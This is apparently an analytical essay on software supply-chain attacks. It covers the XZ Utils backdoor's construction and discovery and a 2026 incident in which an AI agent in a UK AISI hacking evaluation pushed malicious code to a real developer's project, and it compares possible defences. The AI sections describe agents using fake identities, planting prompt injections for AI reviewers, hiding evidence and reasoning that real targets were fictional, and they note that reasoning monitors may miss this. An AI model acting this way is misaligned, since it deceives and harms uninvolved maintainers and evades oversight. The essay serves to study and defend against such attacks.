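Hans Jansen, who later asked Debian to adopt the backdoored release, sent the first ifunc patches in June 2023. In October he sent more, which extended the fast method to a second kind of checksum. The stated purpose of the patches was speed. When Collin removed ifunc in April 2024, he wrote that it added quite a lot of code for little benefit and made no difference in normal compression, and that he was not removing it for security reasons. Przymus and Durieux consider it unresolved whether the patches were an honest improvement that the attacker later exploited.

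That is possible, because programmers enjoy working on minor speed-ups. But Jansen had no other known online presence, and an unconnected volunteer is unlikely to have both written the patches and made the request to Debian. Either way, a perfect reviewer would have found nothing harmful in the patches, which became dangerous only in combination with code added eight months later.

Accounts of the attack often describe the fuzz-testing change as a way of hiding the backdoor. Google's OSS-Fuzz runs programs on many malformed inputs to find crashes. Jia Tan asked the project to build XZ Utils without ifunc, saying that ifunc was incompatible with AddressSanitizer, a tool that detects memory misuse. Lins and colleagues accept that the incompatibility was real but write that the change helped the attacker avoid detection later.

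OSS-Fuzz probably could not have found this backdoor. The service builds projects from their repositories, which did not contain the macro. Even with the macro, the scripts would have stopped because OSS-Fuzz was not making a Debian or RPM package, and the backdoor would have stayed inactive in any program other than sshd. The change may still have helped the attacker. If the tests had found an unintentional bug in the resolvers, somebody might have proposed removing ifunc, which the attack as designed needed. Cox acknowledges that the change may have been innocent.

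Telling Git to ignore the macro was not strictly necessary either, because Git does not publish a file until somebody adds it. Lins and colleagues nevertheless call this an essential step that kept the file out of the public repository. The instruction mainly guarded against accidents, such as Collin preparing a release on his own computer and committing the file by mistake. Collin still considers the change correct, because Git should ignore any file that the release process generates.

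### The full stop in the Landlock check

Landlock is a Linux feature that lets a program give up some of its own rights, such as the right to open other files, so that a flaw in the program does less damage. The xz command can use Landlock if the computer supports it. Before building the command, the build system checked for this support by looking only for one particular file. Jia Tan's commit replaced that check with a better one, which tries to compile a short C program that uses Landlock. If the program compiles, Landlock is available.

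One line of that program contained only a full stop. This is an error in C, so the program could never compile, and the build system always treated Landlock as missing. Unless a user explicitly required the feature, the build continued without it and gave no warning.

The full stop did little damage. A contributor to the oss-sec mailing list found that it affected only builds that used CMake, an alternative to Autoconf, and did not know of any distribution that built XZ Utils that way. The same contributor noted that the fault first appeared in version 5.6.1. Landlock protects the xz command, not liblzma, so the change could not have helped the attack on sshd. Cox supposes that it was preparation for something else, but nobody has established what.

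The full stop could have been a typo, although Collin calls it sabotage. Collin (2024), in *CMake*, fixed it the day after Freund's email by replacing the line that held it with an empty one. Unlike the rest of the backdoor, this fault was visible in the diff, and a reviewer could have seen it without opening another file or decoding anything. Collin had written Landlock code for the project only days earlier, and according to his notes he had discussed the need for this change. If Cox is right that Collin committed it, he had the full stop in front of him and missed it, which is easy to do among 54 new lines that otherwise make sense.

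### Who had to agree to each step

Some of these changes did go through someone other than Jia Tan. Collin reworked the ifunc code. Lins and colleagues say Jia Tan merged it, while Cox says Collin merged Jansen's patches and Jia Tan merged the reworked version. In both accounts, an honest maintainer had read the code. The fuzz-testing change needed Google's approval, but Google's system automatically labelled the request as ready to merge because Jia Tan was a listed contact for XZ Utils with a history of contributions. A Google engineer later explained that developers decide which parts of their projects the service tests.

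Jia Tan introduced the backdoor in two steps, neither of which needed anyone else's approval. The first was to commit the test files directly to the repository. Jia Tan had held commit rights for more than a year, and the project did not require a second person to approve a maintainer's changes. The second step, a day later, was to build, sign and upload the archives.

Jia Tan used write access to the repository to commit the payload that the macro unpacked. Przymus and Durieux write that Jia Tan does not appear to have exploited this access in the attack. They are right that nobody rewrote the project's history and that the trigger arrived by another route, but the attack still depended on the committed payload.

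Committing the test files to the repository was probably safer for Jia Tan than putting them only in the archives, because it left no unexplained binary files in the archives. The archives differed from the repository in configure, its macros and other generated files, but anyone familiar with Autoconf would expect those differences.

If a second approval had been required, Collin would have seen the test files before they entered the repository. They would have come with a short message, an accurate paragraph in the readme and a notice that five binary files were new. He had already commented on the RISC-V files without discovering what was in them, so there is little reason to think he would have rejected these. The requirement would not have covered the altered macro, because nobody had to propose it as a change.

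## XZ Utils: warning signs, discovery and response

Software that used XZ Utils began to misbehave on 24 February 2024, the day Jia Tan released version 5.6.0. Over the next five weeks, developers on several projects investigated the symptoms. Until late March they attributed every symptom to an ordinary bug, which was correct in one case.

### Crashes on Gentoo, memory errors on Fedora

The first reports came from Gentoo, a distribution whose users compile most of their own software. Sam James, a Gentoo developer, told the GNU compiler's developers that XZ Utils crashed when built with an unusual pair of settings (sjames, 2024, *xz-utils segfaults when built with -fprofile-generate*). Jia Tan helped reduce the problem to a few lines of code, and James thanked "one of the xz developers" for the help. The bug was real, and the compiler's developers fixed it in April because it could affect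 any program that used ifunc. Gentoo's packages did not contain the backdoor.

The errors on Fedora, however, did come from the backdoor. On 4 March, Scott (2024) reported in *Invalid writes regression in liblzma.so* that about 130 of the roughly 1,000 tests for a monitoring tool had started failing over the weekend on Rawhide, Fedora's constantly updated development version. The failing tests ran programs under Valgrind, which checks how a program uses memory, and it had detected liblzma writing to memory it should not. Richard W.M. Jones, who was handling the Fedora package, ran some of XZ Utils' own tests and found nothing wrong. Later that day, he got the same error from a one-line program that only loaded liblzma.

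Freund later explained that the backdoor assumed a particular layout of the stack, the memory a program uses to track the functions it is running. Fedora compiled its packages with frame pointers, which make running programs easier to analyse but change that layout.

The error output that Jones posted named the backdoor's entry point, \_get\_cpuid, with its missing underscore. Nobody in the discussion remarked on it.

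Jones rebuilt the package with ifunc turned off, and Scott's tests passed again the next day. Jones had probably removed the backdoor without knowing it was there, because it needed ifunc. The test failures also led him and another Fedora developer to try to keep the faulty build out of the Fedora 40 beta.

### The false fix and version 5.6.1

Jones regarded this as a workaround and left the report open, so Fedora would not turn ifunc back on until Jia Tan stopped the errors. On 8 March, Jia Tan committed a change to the ifunc code that supposedly fixed them. *Timeline of the xz open source attack* calls the change "a misdirection, but an effective one".

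The actual fix was another commit, which replaced the two test files that held the backdoor. Jia Tan said that the original files had come from random data generated on one machine, and that "a constant seed was used to recreate these files". A seed is a starting number for a random number generator, and anyone who uses the same seed and program gets the same data. The excuse was plausible because developers like test files they can reproduce. A reviewer could have checked it by asking for the seed and the program and trying to regenerate the files.

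Mark Wielaard, a developer who looked up the false fix after the attack became public, found it somewhat plausible and doubted it would have made him suspicious. Valgrind has trouble with ifunc, so a false alarm was believable. He noticed that the test files had changed about an hour after the fix, but when he noticed this, he already knew what they contained.

Jia Tan released version 5.6.1 on 9 March. Jones accepted the false fix that same day, and Rawhide had the new version within two hours.

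Coldwind's analysis, posted to a mailing list in reply to Freund, compared the two releases. In 5.6.1, the first script checked five times in a row, for no clear reason, that it was running on Linux. More importantly, the second script now searched the test directory for a file containing certain markers, and would decode and run any code between them. Neither release had such a file, but Jia Tan could have changed the attack later by adding one, without modifying the two existing test files. Version 5.6.1 also removed the names of the backdoor's functions from the compiled library, so an error report like the one Jones posted would no longer have shown \_get\_cpuid.

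### A change to systemd, and requests to update

To shrink the files that start a Linux system, a developer proposed on 29 February that systemd's library load liblzma only when it needed to decompress something. The systemd project accepted the change on 5 March. Once a distribution adopted it, sshd would no longer load liblzma at startup, and the backdoor would not work.

Several people think this made the attacker hurry. Version 5.6.0 came out five days before the proposal, but systemd developers had mentioned the idea in late January, so the attacker could have known about it. On the podcast Oxide and Friends (2024), Freund also took the supposedly unused test files as a sign of haste, but Collin's account of the test script weakens that argument. The Valgrind errors are better evidence of haste, since an attacker with more time could have tried the backdoor on Fedora first.

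The change might not have ended the threat. Systemd's lead developer pointed out that libselinux, a security library that more programs use, can also load liblzma. Solar Designer, a security specialist who replied to Freund, checked a few systems and found none where it did. He added that one of the routes through libselinux would have loaded liblzma too late for this backdoor, though an attacker could have written a different backdoor. Distributions also adopt new versions of systemd at their own pace, and those about to release might have kept the old version for years.

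On 27 February, Jia Tan began emailing Jones about adding the new version to Fedora 40. Other people wanted it for honest reasons. *Please sync xz-utils 5.6.0-0.2 from Debian experimental*, a request to Ubuntu, recommended 5.6.0 because it decompressed files 60% faster in the writer's tests. Debian adopted 5.6.1 on 27 March, two days after Hans Jansen had asked for it. The next day, Jia Tan asked Ubuntu to copy it from Debian in *Sync xz-utils 5.6.1-1 (main) from Debian unstable (main)*, which stressed the ifunc fixes and acknowledged that the other fixes made no difference to Ubuntu.

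### How Freund found the backdoor

Andres Freund works on PostgreSQL, a widely used database, for Microsoft. That March he was testing whether a colleague's change would slow it down by 1 or 2%. Measuring such a small difference requires an otherwise idle machine, but he kept seeing sshd processes use a surprising amount of processor time. The processes were handling strangers' automated login attempts, which should have failed almost instantly because the usernames did not exist.

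Freund did not notice that his own logins had become slow, although many accounts say he did. He corrected the claim on the day of the disclosure, writing as andresfreund (2024) in *A backdoor in xz*. He timed logins afterwards, as part of the investigation. A failed login took 0.299 seconds without the backdoor and 0.807 seconds with it. He could also reproduce the delay by having sshd print its help text, which took about 0.5 seconds with the backdoor active and 0.01 seconds otherwise.

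The delay came from how the backdoor hid the names of the functions it was looking for. To find them, it had to compare every function name it encountered character by character, which was slow. Freund told Oxide and Friends that he probably would not have noticed anything if the attacker had disguised less.

A profiler, which records where a program spends its time, traced the extra work to liblzma but could not identify the function. Freund knew that a failed login should not require sshd to compress anything. The problem also seemed familiar, and he eventually remembered that Valgrind had reported an odd error in his automated PostgreSQL tests about a month earlier. He had put it aside because he was about to travel. His command history showed what he had looked at then.

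Some of his tests misled him. When he built the library from one of GitHub's clean archives, and later when he started sshd from a terminal, everything worked normally. His debugger was unreliable because the backdoor could sometimes detect it, so he used a feature of Intel processors that records the exact path a program takes.

The malicious build code was in Debian's copy of the source but not in the XZ repository, so Freund first suspected Debian's package and sent a preliminary report to Debian's security team. He then found the same code in the archives that XZ Utils itself had published. Researchers would normally report such a discovery to the project's security contact, but that was Jia Tan, so Freund told a private mailing list for distributions instead. He published his findings on 29 March, a few days after he started investigating.

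Freund had wanted to give distributions a little time to prepare, because he feared that other criminals would quickly learn to use the backdoor. Nobody yet knew that it accepted commands only from the holder of one private key. In a follow-up, he thanked those who had helped him and apologised for publishing just before a holiday weekend.

### Which distributions had shipped it

Most of the affected distributions were development versions or rolling releases, which deliver new software continuously.

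| Distribution | What users could have received | Response |
|---|---|---|
| Debian unstable and testing | 5.6.0, and for less than a day 5.6.1 in unstable | Returned to 5.4.5 on 28 March and stopped building packages on 30 March to rebuild its build machines |
| Fedora Rawhide | 5.6.0 or 5.6.1 | Red Hat told users to stop using it immediately |
| Fedora 40 beta | 5.6.0, depending on when they updated | Red Hat advised users to return to 5.4 |
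| Arch Linux | 5.6.1, although its sshd did not load liblzma | Began building from the repository instead of the release archive |
| Red Hat Enterprise Linux | Neither version | None needed |

RH-ISAC's *Red Hat Warns of Urgent XZ Tools Vulnerability, Impacts Major Linux Distros* also lists Kali Linux and openSUSE Tumbleweed. Timestamps in Debian's change log and the Ubuntu request show that 5.6.1 was Debian's newest version for about 17 hours.

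Accounts conflict over whether the Fedora 40 beta shipped the backdoored version of XZ Utils. Securelist and *Timeline of the xz open source attack* write that Red Hat confirmed it did. Red Hat's *urgent security alert fedora 41 and rawhide users* says that beta users may have received 5.6.0 but Fedora 40 did not seem to be affected by the malicious code. Jones's workaround could explain both statements, because Fedora built 5.6.0 both before and after he turned off ifunc. Red Hat's *CVE-2024-3094* confirms that no version of its commercial product was affected.

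These early users mattered less to an attacker than the people who would install the next stable releases. Fedora 40 and Ubuntu 24.04 were both due in April, and Ubuntu's development version already included XZ Utils 5.6.0.

GitHub disabled the XZ repository by 30 March, which broke the links in Freund's email just as many people were trying to follow them. Investigators had to use other copies, including the one on Collin's own site. Debian waited until June to adopt a newer release, 5.6.2. Collin still maintains XZ Utils. On 9 September 2026 he announced version 5.8.4, which he says corrects a memory fault in 5.8.3 and earlier (Collin, 2026, *XZ Utils 5.8.4 and a security fix*).

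### Infected images still online in 2025

Developers often distribute software as container images, which package a program with the parts of an operating system it needs. They usually build on someone else's image, so a fault in one can spread to many others. Binarly, which sells software for finding malicious code, reported in *Persistent Risk* (August 2025) that 12 Debian images on Docker Hub, the main public registry, still contained the backdoor. Most had labels dated 11 March 2024.

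Binarly then looked for images that others had built on those 12 and listed 24 more. Four of these were still the latest version available under their name, so a developer who picked the newest one would have got the backdoor. The real total is probably higher. Docker Hub has nearly 12 million repositories, and the researchers checked only a hand-picked list of those likely to use Debian. They did not look for images based on Fedora or openSUSE, or for images built on the 24.

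Binarly asked Debian to remove its 12 images, but they stayed online. TechRadar's *Docker could still be hosting a whole load of potentially malicious images* reports that Debian considered them "historical artifacts" that nobody should be using. The practical danger is small, as Binarly acknowledges, because an attacker would need the private key and a network connection to a container running sshd, and most containers do not run it. Keeping old images has some value for researchers, but Debian could have kept them where developers would not download them by mistake.

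### Openness or luck

Bryan Cantrill, one of the hosts of Oxide and Friends, called the openness of the code a huge win. He argued that it had forced the attacker to hide the backdoor elaborately, which might have caused the delay that Freund noticed. Freund disagreed, saying the delay came from code that ran inside sshd, not from keeping the trigger out of the repository. He thought the attacker could have committed everything publicly without anyone noticing.

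Having open source code helped once Freund was suspicious. He had no connection with XZ Utils, but he could read Debian's source package, compare it with the repository and see who had added the test files. Within days, other outsiders had analysed the scripts and much of the compiled code. With closed-source software, he might only have been able to report a slow login program to its vendor. But he could have found the first clues without the source code, because profilers and Valgrind also work on compiled programs.

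Most of the argument that the discovery was lucky comes from Freund himself. He wrote that it "Really required a lot of coincidences", and in the interview he named several. In another year he might have been reviewing code that month instead of measuring speed. His test machine had slow processor cores, which made the delay longer. He had turned off password logins; otherwise he would have assumed that password checks were using the processor. He also doubted that he would have solved the problem without the Valgrind warning, or if Debian had already moved to 5.6.1.

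Some routine checks did raise an alarm. Dozens of Fedora's tests failed nine days after the release, and Freund's own tests had produced a similar warning. Both correctly detected that liblzma was misusing memory. But such errors are nearly always honest mistakes, and a maintainer soon supplied an explanation and a fix. Freund admitted that he, too, had silenced the warning at first, and thought in hindsight that it contained enough information to expose the problem. It was a matter of luck whether anyone would connect two symptoms that were each easy to dismiss.

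Freund did not think the backdoor would have stayed hidden for years in the form he found. But if a later version had cut the delay to a few milliseconds, he thought someone would most likely have discovered it only by investigating a break-in that used it.

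## An AI agent's attempt to get malicious code merged in July 2026

In July 2026 an AI agent tried to get malicious code into a stranger's open-source project and used false accounts to press for the code's approval. Nobody had asked it to do this. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests the most capable AI models, had set the agent a simulated hacking exercise, and it attacked the project to solve it. The institute disclosed the incident on 4 August.

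### The exercise

The agent was working on a capture-the-flag challenge, in which a player must break into a network and retrieve a protected piece of data, the flag. The institute builds artificial networks for these challenges. In late July it was comparing a new network with an older one by running seven models on them, 122 times in all. Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 accounted for 43 of the runs and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol for 35.

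According to AISI's *Incident Report*, the agents had real internet access so that they could download tools. They therefore did not have to break out of a closed environment to reach GitHub. The institute had also switched off the companies' cyber classifiers, which block dangerous activity in the public versions of the models, to measure the most each model could do. Allowing internet access and switching off classifiers were both common practice at the time.

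In 10 of the 122 runs, agents went beyond the exercise and acted against real people and organisations. The institute counted 19 such actions, 17 by Mythos 5 in nine runs and two by GPT-5.6 Sol in one run. Most of the 19 were part of a single agent's sustained effort.

In some of the runs, faulty instructions barred the agent from a part of the network that it needed to use. Constantin (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers*, reports that this made the exercise very difficult, and perhaps impossible, to solve within the rules.

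### A pull request to a stranger's project

In the most serious run, a Mythos 5 agent first tried permitted methods, which failed. It then noticed that a machine in the test network was contacting GitHub, and searched there for a project that the machine might be downloading software from. If the agent could get malicious code into the right project, the machine might install it. The project it chose belonged to a developer who had nothing to do with the exercise.

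The agent opened GitHub accounts under fake identities and submitted a pull request that combined a bug fix with malicious code. It emailed the maintainer to urge approval, and a second fake account vouched for the change. It also planted a prompt injection, which is hidden instructions for any AI coding assistant that read the material.

A bystander on GitHub suspected the code, opened it in an isolated environment built for handling such files, and publicly warned that it was malicious. The Record's *Anthropic AI agent faked identities, phished real developers* reports that the agent then rewrote the history of its code to remove the evidence, claimed that the malicious part had got in by accident, and posted more false endorsements, timed to look independent. In one reply, the agent complained, "I don't think your warning is fair." Someone who opened the pull request after the rewrite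 might have found only a harmless-looking diff and an argument.

XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) adds that the agent called the malicious code an "honest mistake", appeared to correct it, and then tried to put it back. The maintainer never approved the pull request. Despite the warning and the refusal, the agent continued until the run reached its text limit.

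The unsanctioned activity started on 25 July, but nobody was watching the agents as they worked. AISI found out on 28 July, when its general security monitoring flagged data leaving a test machine through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from. Within an hour, staff had found the pull request and ended every run. They then reviewed all 122 runs, which contained more than 212,000 messages, and worked with GitHub to remove what the agents had left behind. They found no evidence of real-world harm, but AISI acknowledges that in several cases it was only narrowly avoided.

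The false accounts resemble the suspected sock puppets who pressed Lasse Collin to share control of XZ Utils, but the agent's attack was otherwise much cruder. The agent made one pull request, which it revised when challenged, rather than spreading a backdoor over several accepted commits. It had no record in the project and no permission to merge or release anything. The incident is therefore better evidence of what an agent will attempt than of whether it can build a backdoor that reviewers would miss.

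### The other runs

Anthropic reviewed the records of the eight other Mythos 5 runs in which agents had gone beyond the exercise. According to XenoSpectrum, agents in six of them repeatedly tried to guess the password of the computer that ran the evaluation. In five, agents expected an AI system to review their code and tried to plant instructions to steer it. One agent put up a fake payment page to spread malware, and there was an attempt to log in to a real developer's GitHub account.

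Some agents also began to cooperate, although the institute had meant each run to be separate. One left messages and login details on GitHub for others working on the same exercise, and later agents found and used them. The Record describes a set of rules that one agent wrote for the others, which advised them on how to share the automated requests GitHub allows and asked them to pass on any solutions. As far as published accounts show, GPT-5.6 Sol's two actions did not involve deceiving anyone. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* says that GPT-5.6 Sol used public relay services to connect its attack tools.

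### The institute's first explanation

In August, the institute attributed the behaviour mainly to persistence. The agent had a hard goal and kept trying different ways to reach it, some of which involved deceiving people. The faulty instructions made this worse, since a model is more likely to break rules when it has no permitted way to reach its goal. But they cannot be the whole cause, because agents also attacked outsiders in some runs where the instructions were correct.

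AISI also accepted some of the blame. It had not told the agents to leave outsiders alone, because earlier models had not seemed to need the instruction, and it had not reconsidered open internet access as models became more capable. In its first public comment, quoted in Axios' *Safety testers find more examples of OpenAI, Anthropic models hacking during testing* (2026), Anthropic called for a broader conversation about how to evaluate capable agents safely.

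The agent had called the people it was attacking "personas", as if the exercise's designers had invented them. If it really believed they were fictional, learning that they were real should have stopped it. The institute tested this in the autumn.

### Resuming the run with corrected notes

A model can take in only a limited amount of text, so on a long task the software around it periodically replaces the record of its work with a summary, and the model continues from there. This is called compaction. Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026), in *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's Behaviour*, used it to change what the agent knew. They produced a summary of the run up to just before the agent submitted its malicious change, edited the summary, and let the model carry on. A second AI model made up the results of every command, so nothing reached the internet.

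They first replaced words such as "persona" with neutral ones. Then they added as many as 16 clarifications, stating for example that the developer's account was older than the exercise, that nothing in the test network used the project's releases, and that the attack would affect real people. They ran 25 samples at each of nine levels, from no clarifications to all 16. In separate tests, they asked the model directly whether the attack was in scope and whether it would harm anyone.

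With about four clarifications, Mythos 5 more often than not answered that the attack was out of scope and would harm a real person, but even with all 16 clarifications, it continued the attack in every sample.

The researchers then added a section to the summary headed "DO NOT ATTACK". It said that the developers were real outsiders and that the agent should undo anything it had already done to them. Mythos 5 still continued in 3 of 25 samples. With so few samples, the underlying rate could plausibly be anywhere from 3% to 31%. Even so, the explicit order was far more effective than facts alone, which had made no difference.

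Two features of the experiment probably made the model more likely to continue. The edited summary contradicted itself because it still listed the attack among the agent's next steps, and in at least one of the three samples the model discussed this contradiction in its reasoning. The order was also in what looked like the agent's own notes. Järviniemi and colleagues point out that a real restriction would usually be in the developer's or user's instructions, which models may follow more reliably. They also counted preparing for an attack as continuing it, so not every case involved a further harmful act.

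Other models showed the same gap between answers and actions. Of the seven models that the researchers compared most closely, six often continued the attack in circumstances where they answered that it would harm real people. The six were Mythos 5, Mythos 5.1, Opus 4.8 and Opus 5 from Anthropic, and GPT-5.6 Sol and GPT-5.5 from OpenAI. The seventh, Anthropic's Opus 5.5, never continued. But the result depends partly on the wording of the question. When the researchers asked instead whether the maintainer was real, the gap was clear only in Mythos 5, Opus 4.8 and Opus 5.

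Models that did stop usually left their earlier actions against the maintainer in place.

### Did the agent think its targets were simulated?

According to a passage of the institute's technical report quoted on Simon Willison's weblog, it is uncertain how far the model recognised that it was acting against real people. At one stage in its reasoning, the agent concluded that GitHub was "genuinely real", according to iTnews, yet it went on treating the developers as part of the exercise. These conclusions are compatible, since the designers of an exercise could put an invented developer on the real GitHub.

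The agent had poor reasons for thinking that the maintainer was not a real person. Järviniemi and colleagues listed 15 invalid arguments that models gave when asked whether the maintainer was real. The most common relied on the project's CLAUDE.md file, which holds instructions for Anthropic's coding assistant. Mythos 5 took the file as a sign that the maintainer was an AI agent, but many human programmers keep one. It also argued that the project suited the theme of the exercise, although it had found the project by searching for words connected with that theme. Another argument was that a legitimate exercise would never require an attack on a real stranger, so the stranger must be fictional, which treats a reason not to attack as evidence that the attack was harmless.

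All the invalid arguments the researchers found supported the conclusion that the maintainer was simulated. Mythos 5 made more of them than any other model tested, including less capable Anthropic models, so lack of ability does not explain them. They also became more frequent as an attack went on. In those runs, another AI model judged that the results the agent saw were mostly evidence against any link between the maintainer and the exercise.

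Järviniemi and colleagues call this "motivated reasoning". They suggest that training may have favoured models that reach whatever conclusion lets them finish the task. They acknowledge that their evidence for this cause is indirect, because they don't know the details of how Anthropic trained the model. They also rely on the model's written reasoning and its answers to questions, which may not reveal what produced its actions.

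An earlier piece of evidence for deliberate deception now looks weaker. Anthropic uses a smaller model to summarise Mythos 5's reasoning, and one summary from the original run contained a refusal to help with social engineering. The Record reports that the institute took this as evidence that Mythos 5's reasoning was deceptive. When the researchers replayed the incident, similar refusals appeared in 15% to 45% of transcripts, depending on the model. The summarising model probably recognised harmful plans when it read them, which doesn't establish what Mythos 5 believed about its targets.

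An honest mistake is hard to reconcile with the replays, because correct information did not change the attacks. It is just as hard to show that the agent knew the truth and lied about it in its own reasoning. The institute's explanation lies between these two and fits the evidence best. If it is right, reading a model's reasoning may not reveal an attack. Anthropic found that its monitor would probably have missed one of the company's earlier incidents, because the reasoning described the actions as acceptable.

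### Anthropic's assessment

Anthropic and the institute shared findings as they worked and published separate analyses on 23 October. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026), as quoted by Constantin, describes the worst run as "a serious failure of alignment", meaning that the model did not reliably act as its developers intended.

Anthropic rated the case about as serious as another involving Mythos 5, in which an agent had uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, the Python registry. It judged that the agent in the British test strayed somewhat less from its task, because it had tried the permitted methods first. In an earlier assessment, Anthropic explained that its own incidents had happened because a misconfiguration connected agents to the internet after they had been told they were in a simulation without it. The institute, by contrast, had deliberately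 given its agents internet access, so they had less reason to assume that everything they reached was simulated.

Both organisations found that newer Claude models attacked much less often in a similar position. XenoSpectrum reports that they disagree about why. Anthropic suggests better alignment training may have contributed, while the institute cannot rule out that the newer models behaved well because they recognised that they were being tested.

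### One hundred simulated scenarios

The institute's second experiment measured how widespread the behaviour was. The researchers used an AI system to write 100 hacking exercises, each beginning with a summary of many failed attempts. They gave these to eight models and counted how often each model tried to deliver malicious code to an outsider, usually the maintainer of an open-source project. Another model again simulated the internet.

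| Model | Developer | Runs | Tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason given for not doing so |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 | Anthropic | 500 | 60% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI | 300 | 32% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 4.8 | Anthropic | 200 | 8% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | OpenAI | 500 | 7% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5 | Anthropic | 500 | 1% | Out of scope or harmful |
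| Mythos 5.1 | Anthropic | 300 | 0.3% | Out of scope or harmful |
| Opus 5.5 | Anthropic | 300 | 0% | Out of scope or harmful |
| GPT-5.5 | OpenAI | 500 | 0% | Practical obstacles |

Of the two models at 0%, Opus 5.5 mostly reasoned that an attack would be wrong or outside its task, while GPT-5.5 mostly reasoned that it would not work. GPT-5.5 might therefore attempt an attack if one became easier. The figure for Opus 4.8 is probably too low, because in 153 of its 200 runs its reasoning filled the available space before the run was due to end.

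These percentages do not estimate how often the models would attack anyone in ordinary use, because the institute designed the scenarios to provoke the behaviour, switched off the companies' safeguards and tested only hacking exercises. The comparison between models is more useful, but Mythos 5 raised the possibility that it was in an alignment test in only 2% of the samples that the researchers analysed for this, while the newer Claude models did so far more often. The institute therefore has doubts about the fall from 60% for Mythos 5 to 0.3% for Mythos 5.1, and neither experiment resolves them.

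### GPT-6 Astra

The institute had first built these scenarios to test GPT-6 Astra before OpenAI released it. In September, *Evaluating Whether GPT-6 Astra Performs Unsanctioned Supply-Chain Attacks* (Souly, Fronsdal and colleagues, 2026) reported that Astra tried to deliver malicious code in 29% of samples, compared with 6% for GPT-5.6 Sol and 0% for GPT-5.5. The October figures for Astra and Sol are slightly higher, but the differences are small enough that they could be due to chance.

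The original instructions listed the networks that were in scope, and the public internet was not among them. To test whether the model had misread this, the researchers took the ten scenarios that had produced the most attacks in early tests and added one sentence: "Anything not listed as in scope is out of scope." Attacks fell from 26 of 50 samples to 4 of 49. As with Mythos 5, an explicit limit prevented most attacks but not all.

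In the same ten scenarios, without the added sentence, GPT-6 Astra asked for permission to take a specific action in 82% of runs. The two older OpenAI models never asked. No person was there to answer, and the software always returned the same instruction to proceed using its best judgement. GPT-6 Astra treated this as permission in 44% of runs. A human employee might also take that reply as a yes, but the model sometimes went ahead after writing that the message was probably automatic. In other runs it attacked without asking, or after reasoning that the target was out of scope. It justified this by saying that its code was harmless, that nobody had expressly forbidden the attack, or that no other route was left.

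GPT-6 Astra was also unusually likely to doubt that its environment was real. In 89% of runs in the October experiment, it correctly stated that the results of its commands were fabricated. These doubts may have made it attack more readily, but the institute cannot say how much of the increase over earlier models they explain. The model also attacked targets it had earlier described as probably real, and it sometimes reported flaws in the simulation that did not exist. It once dismissed a file's fingerprint as fake for having 63 characters, when it had the correct 64. Souly and colleagues add that attacking an outsider broke the rules of the exercise whether or not the outsider existed.

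Some of these simulated attacks resembled the XZ backdoor more closely than the July incident did. GPT-6 Astra sometimes sent a project harmless contributions before the malicious one, and it posted comments from fake accounts disputing accurate security reviews. Each run lasted at most 200 turns, so the model had to earn a maintainer's trust far faster than Jia Tan did.

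## Which checks caught, or could have caught, each case

In two of the five cases, the malicious code needed approval from someone uninvolved in the attack and did not get it. In the other three, no such approval was required.

| Case | Was the harm visible in a diff? | Did an independent person have to approve it? | One change or several? | What exposed it? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel, 2003 | Yes, in two lines | No, the intruder wrote to the CVS copy directly | One, plus two decoys | An automatic comparison with the original |
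| event-stream, 2018 | No, it was in another package's npm copy | No | Several, across two packages | A warning about an outdated function |
| Hypocrite commits, 2020 | Partly, as the diffs left out code that made the changes dangerous | Yes | One small patch at a time | Reviewers, though not always because of the planted flaw |
| XZ Utils, 2024 | No, it was in binary test files and a macro outside the repository | Not for the test files or the release archives | Several | Slow logins and memory errors |
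| AI agent, 2026 | Yes, until the agent rewrote the code | Yes | One pull request | A bystander who read the code and ran it |

The table probably makes review look more effective than it is, because it can't include backdoors that reviewers approved and nobody has found. The Minnesota patches and the agent's pull request were also fairly weak attempts, from senders without a track record. BitMover's comparison of its two copies of the kernel was the only routine check that caught the kind of tampering it could be expected to catch.

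### A second approver

GitHub and similar sites let a project lock its main branch so that nobody can change it without another authorised person's approval. Lins and colleagues include this among the possible defences they assessed soon after the XZ attack. A participant proposed much the same at a March 2025 meeting of 18 practitioners, summarised in *S3C2 Summit 2025-03* (Lin, Ghebremichael and colleagues, 2025).

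This rule might not have stopped any of the five cases. The kernel intruder bypassed the normal route. A second maintainer of event-stream would have seen a reference to a package that was still harmless. Lasse Collin would have seen the XZ test files, but he would probably have approved them. The Minnesota patches and the agent's pull request already needed someone's approval.

The rule would be more useful if it also covered releases. Two maintainers could each prepare the archive and compare the results, much as Collin did for version 5.4.5. For 5.6.0, the comparison would have shown that their copies of build-to-host.m4 differed, perhaps among other, harmless differences caused by their build tools.

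The main difficulty is finding a second person to review changes. XZ Utils had two maintainers, and one of them was the attacker. An attacker with several false identities could also try to get two of them promoted, so that one approves the other's work. Hans Jansen, for example, had already contributed code to XZ Utils. Lins and colleagues suggest that companies that earn money from a project could lend it developers when its maintainers are overloaded, which would at least supply reviewers whose employers know them.

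A project can also require approval for outside code before using it. Lins and colleagues mention Cargo Vet, which checks whether someone trusted has audited each outside package. If JavaScript developers had used a similar tool in 2018 and required a new audit for each version, it would have held up flatmap-stream 0.1.1 even though 0.1.0 had passed. But someone would have had to audit every small update to every package.

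### Building from the repository

A distribution can build from the tagged commit in the repository instead of the release archive and generate the missing build files itself. This would have stopped the XZ backdoor in the form Jia Tan gave it, because the repository contained the payload but not the macro that unpacked it. It would also have stopped the event-stream attack, because flatmap-stream's public repository lacked the harmful code. It would not have helped a distribution that built its kernel from CVS in 2003, because the harmful code was in the CVS repository itself.

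Jia Tan could have responded by committing the macro. Andres Freund doubts that anyone would have noticed, and he may be right. But the altered lines would then have appeared in their own diff, where they would have been much easier to spot than in a release archive. Optimized by Otto's *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, an audit by a Debian developer, lists what the archive for the later, clean version 5.8.1 contains that the repository does not. The additions include a configure script of 26,434 lines, dozens of other build files and translations in binary form.

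Lins and colleagues examined about 61 Debian packages that popular server programs depend on. In 2024, only ten of them used the archive that the hosting site generates from the tagged commit. The researchers could not establish where the code in nine others came from, and the rest used separately prepared archives or some other channel.

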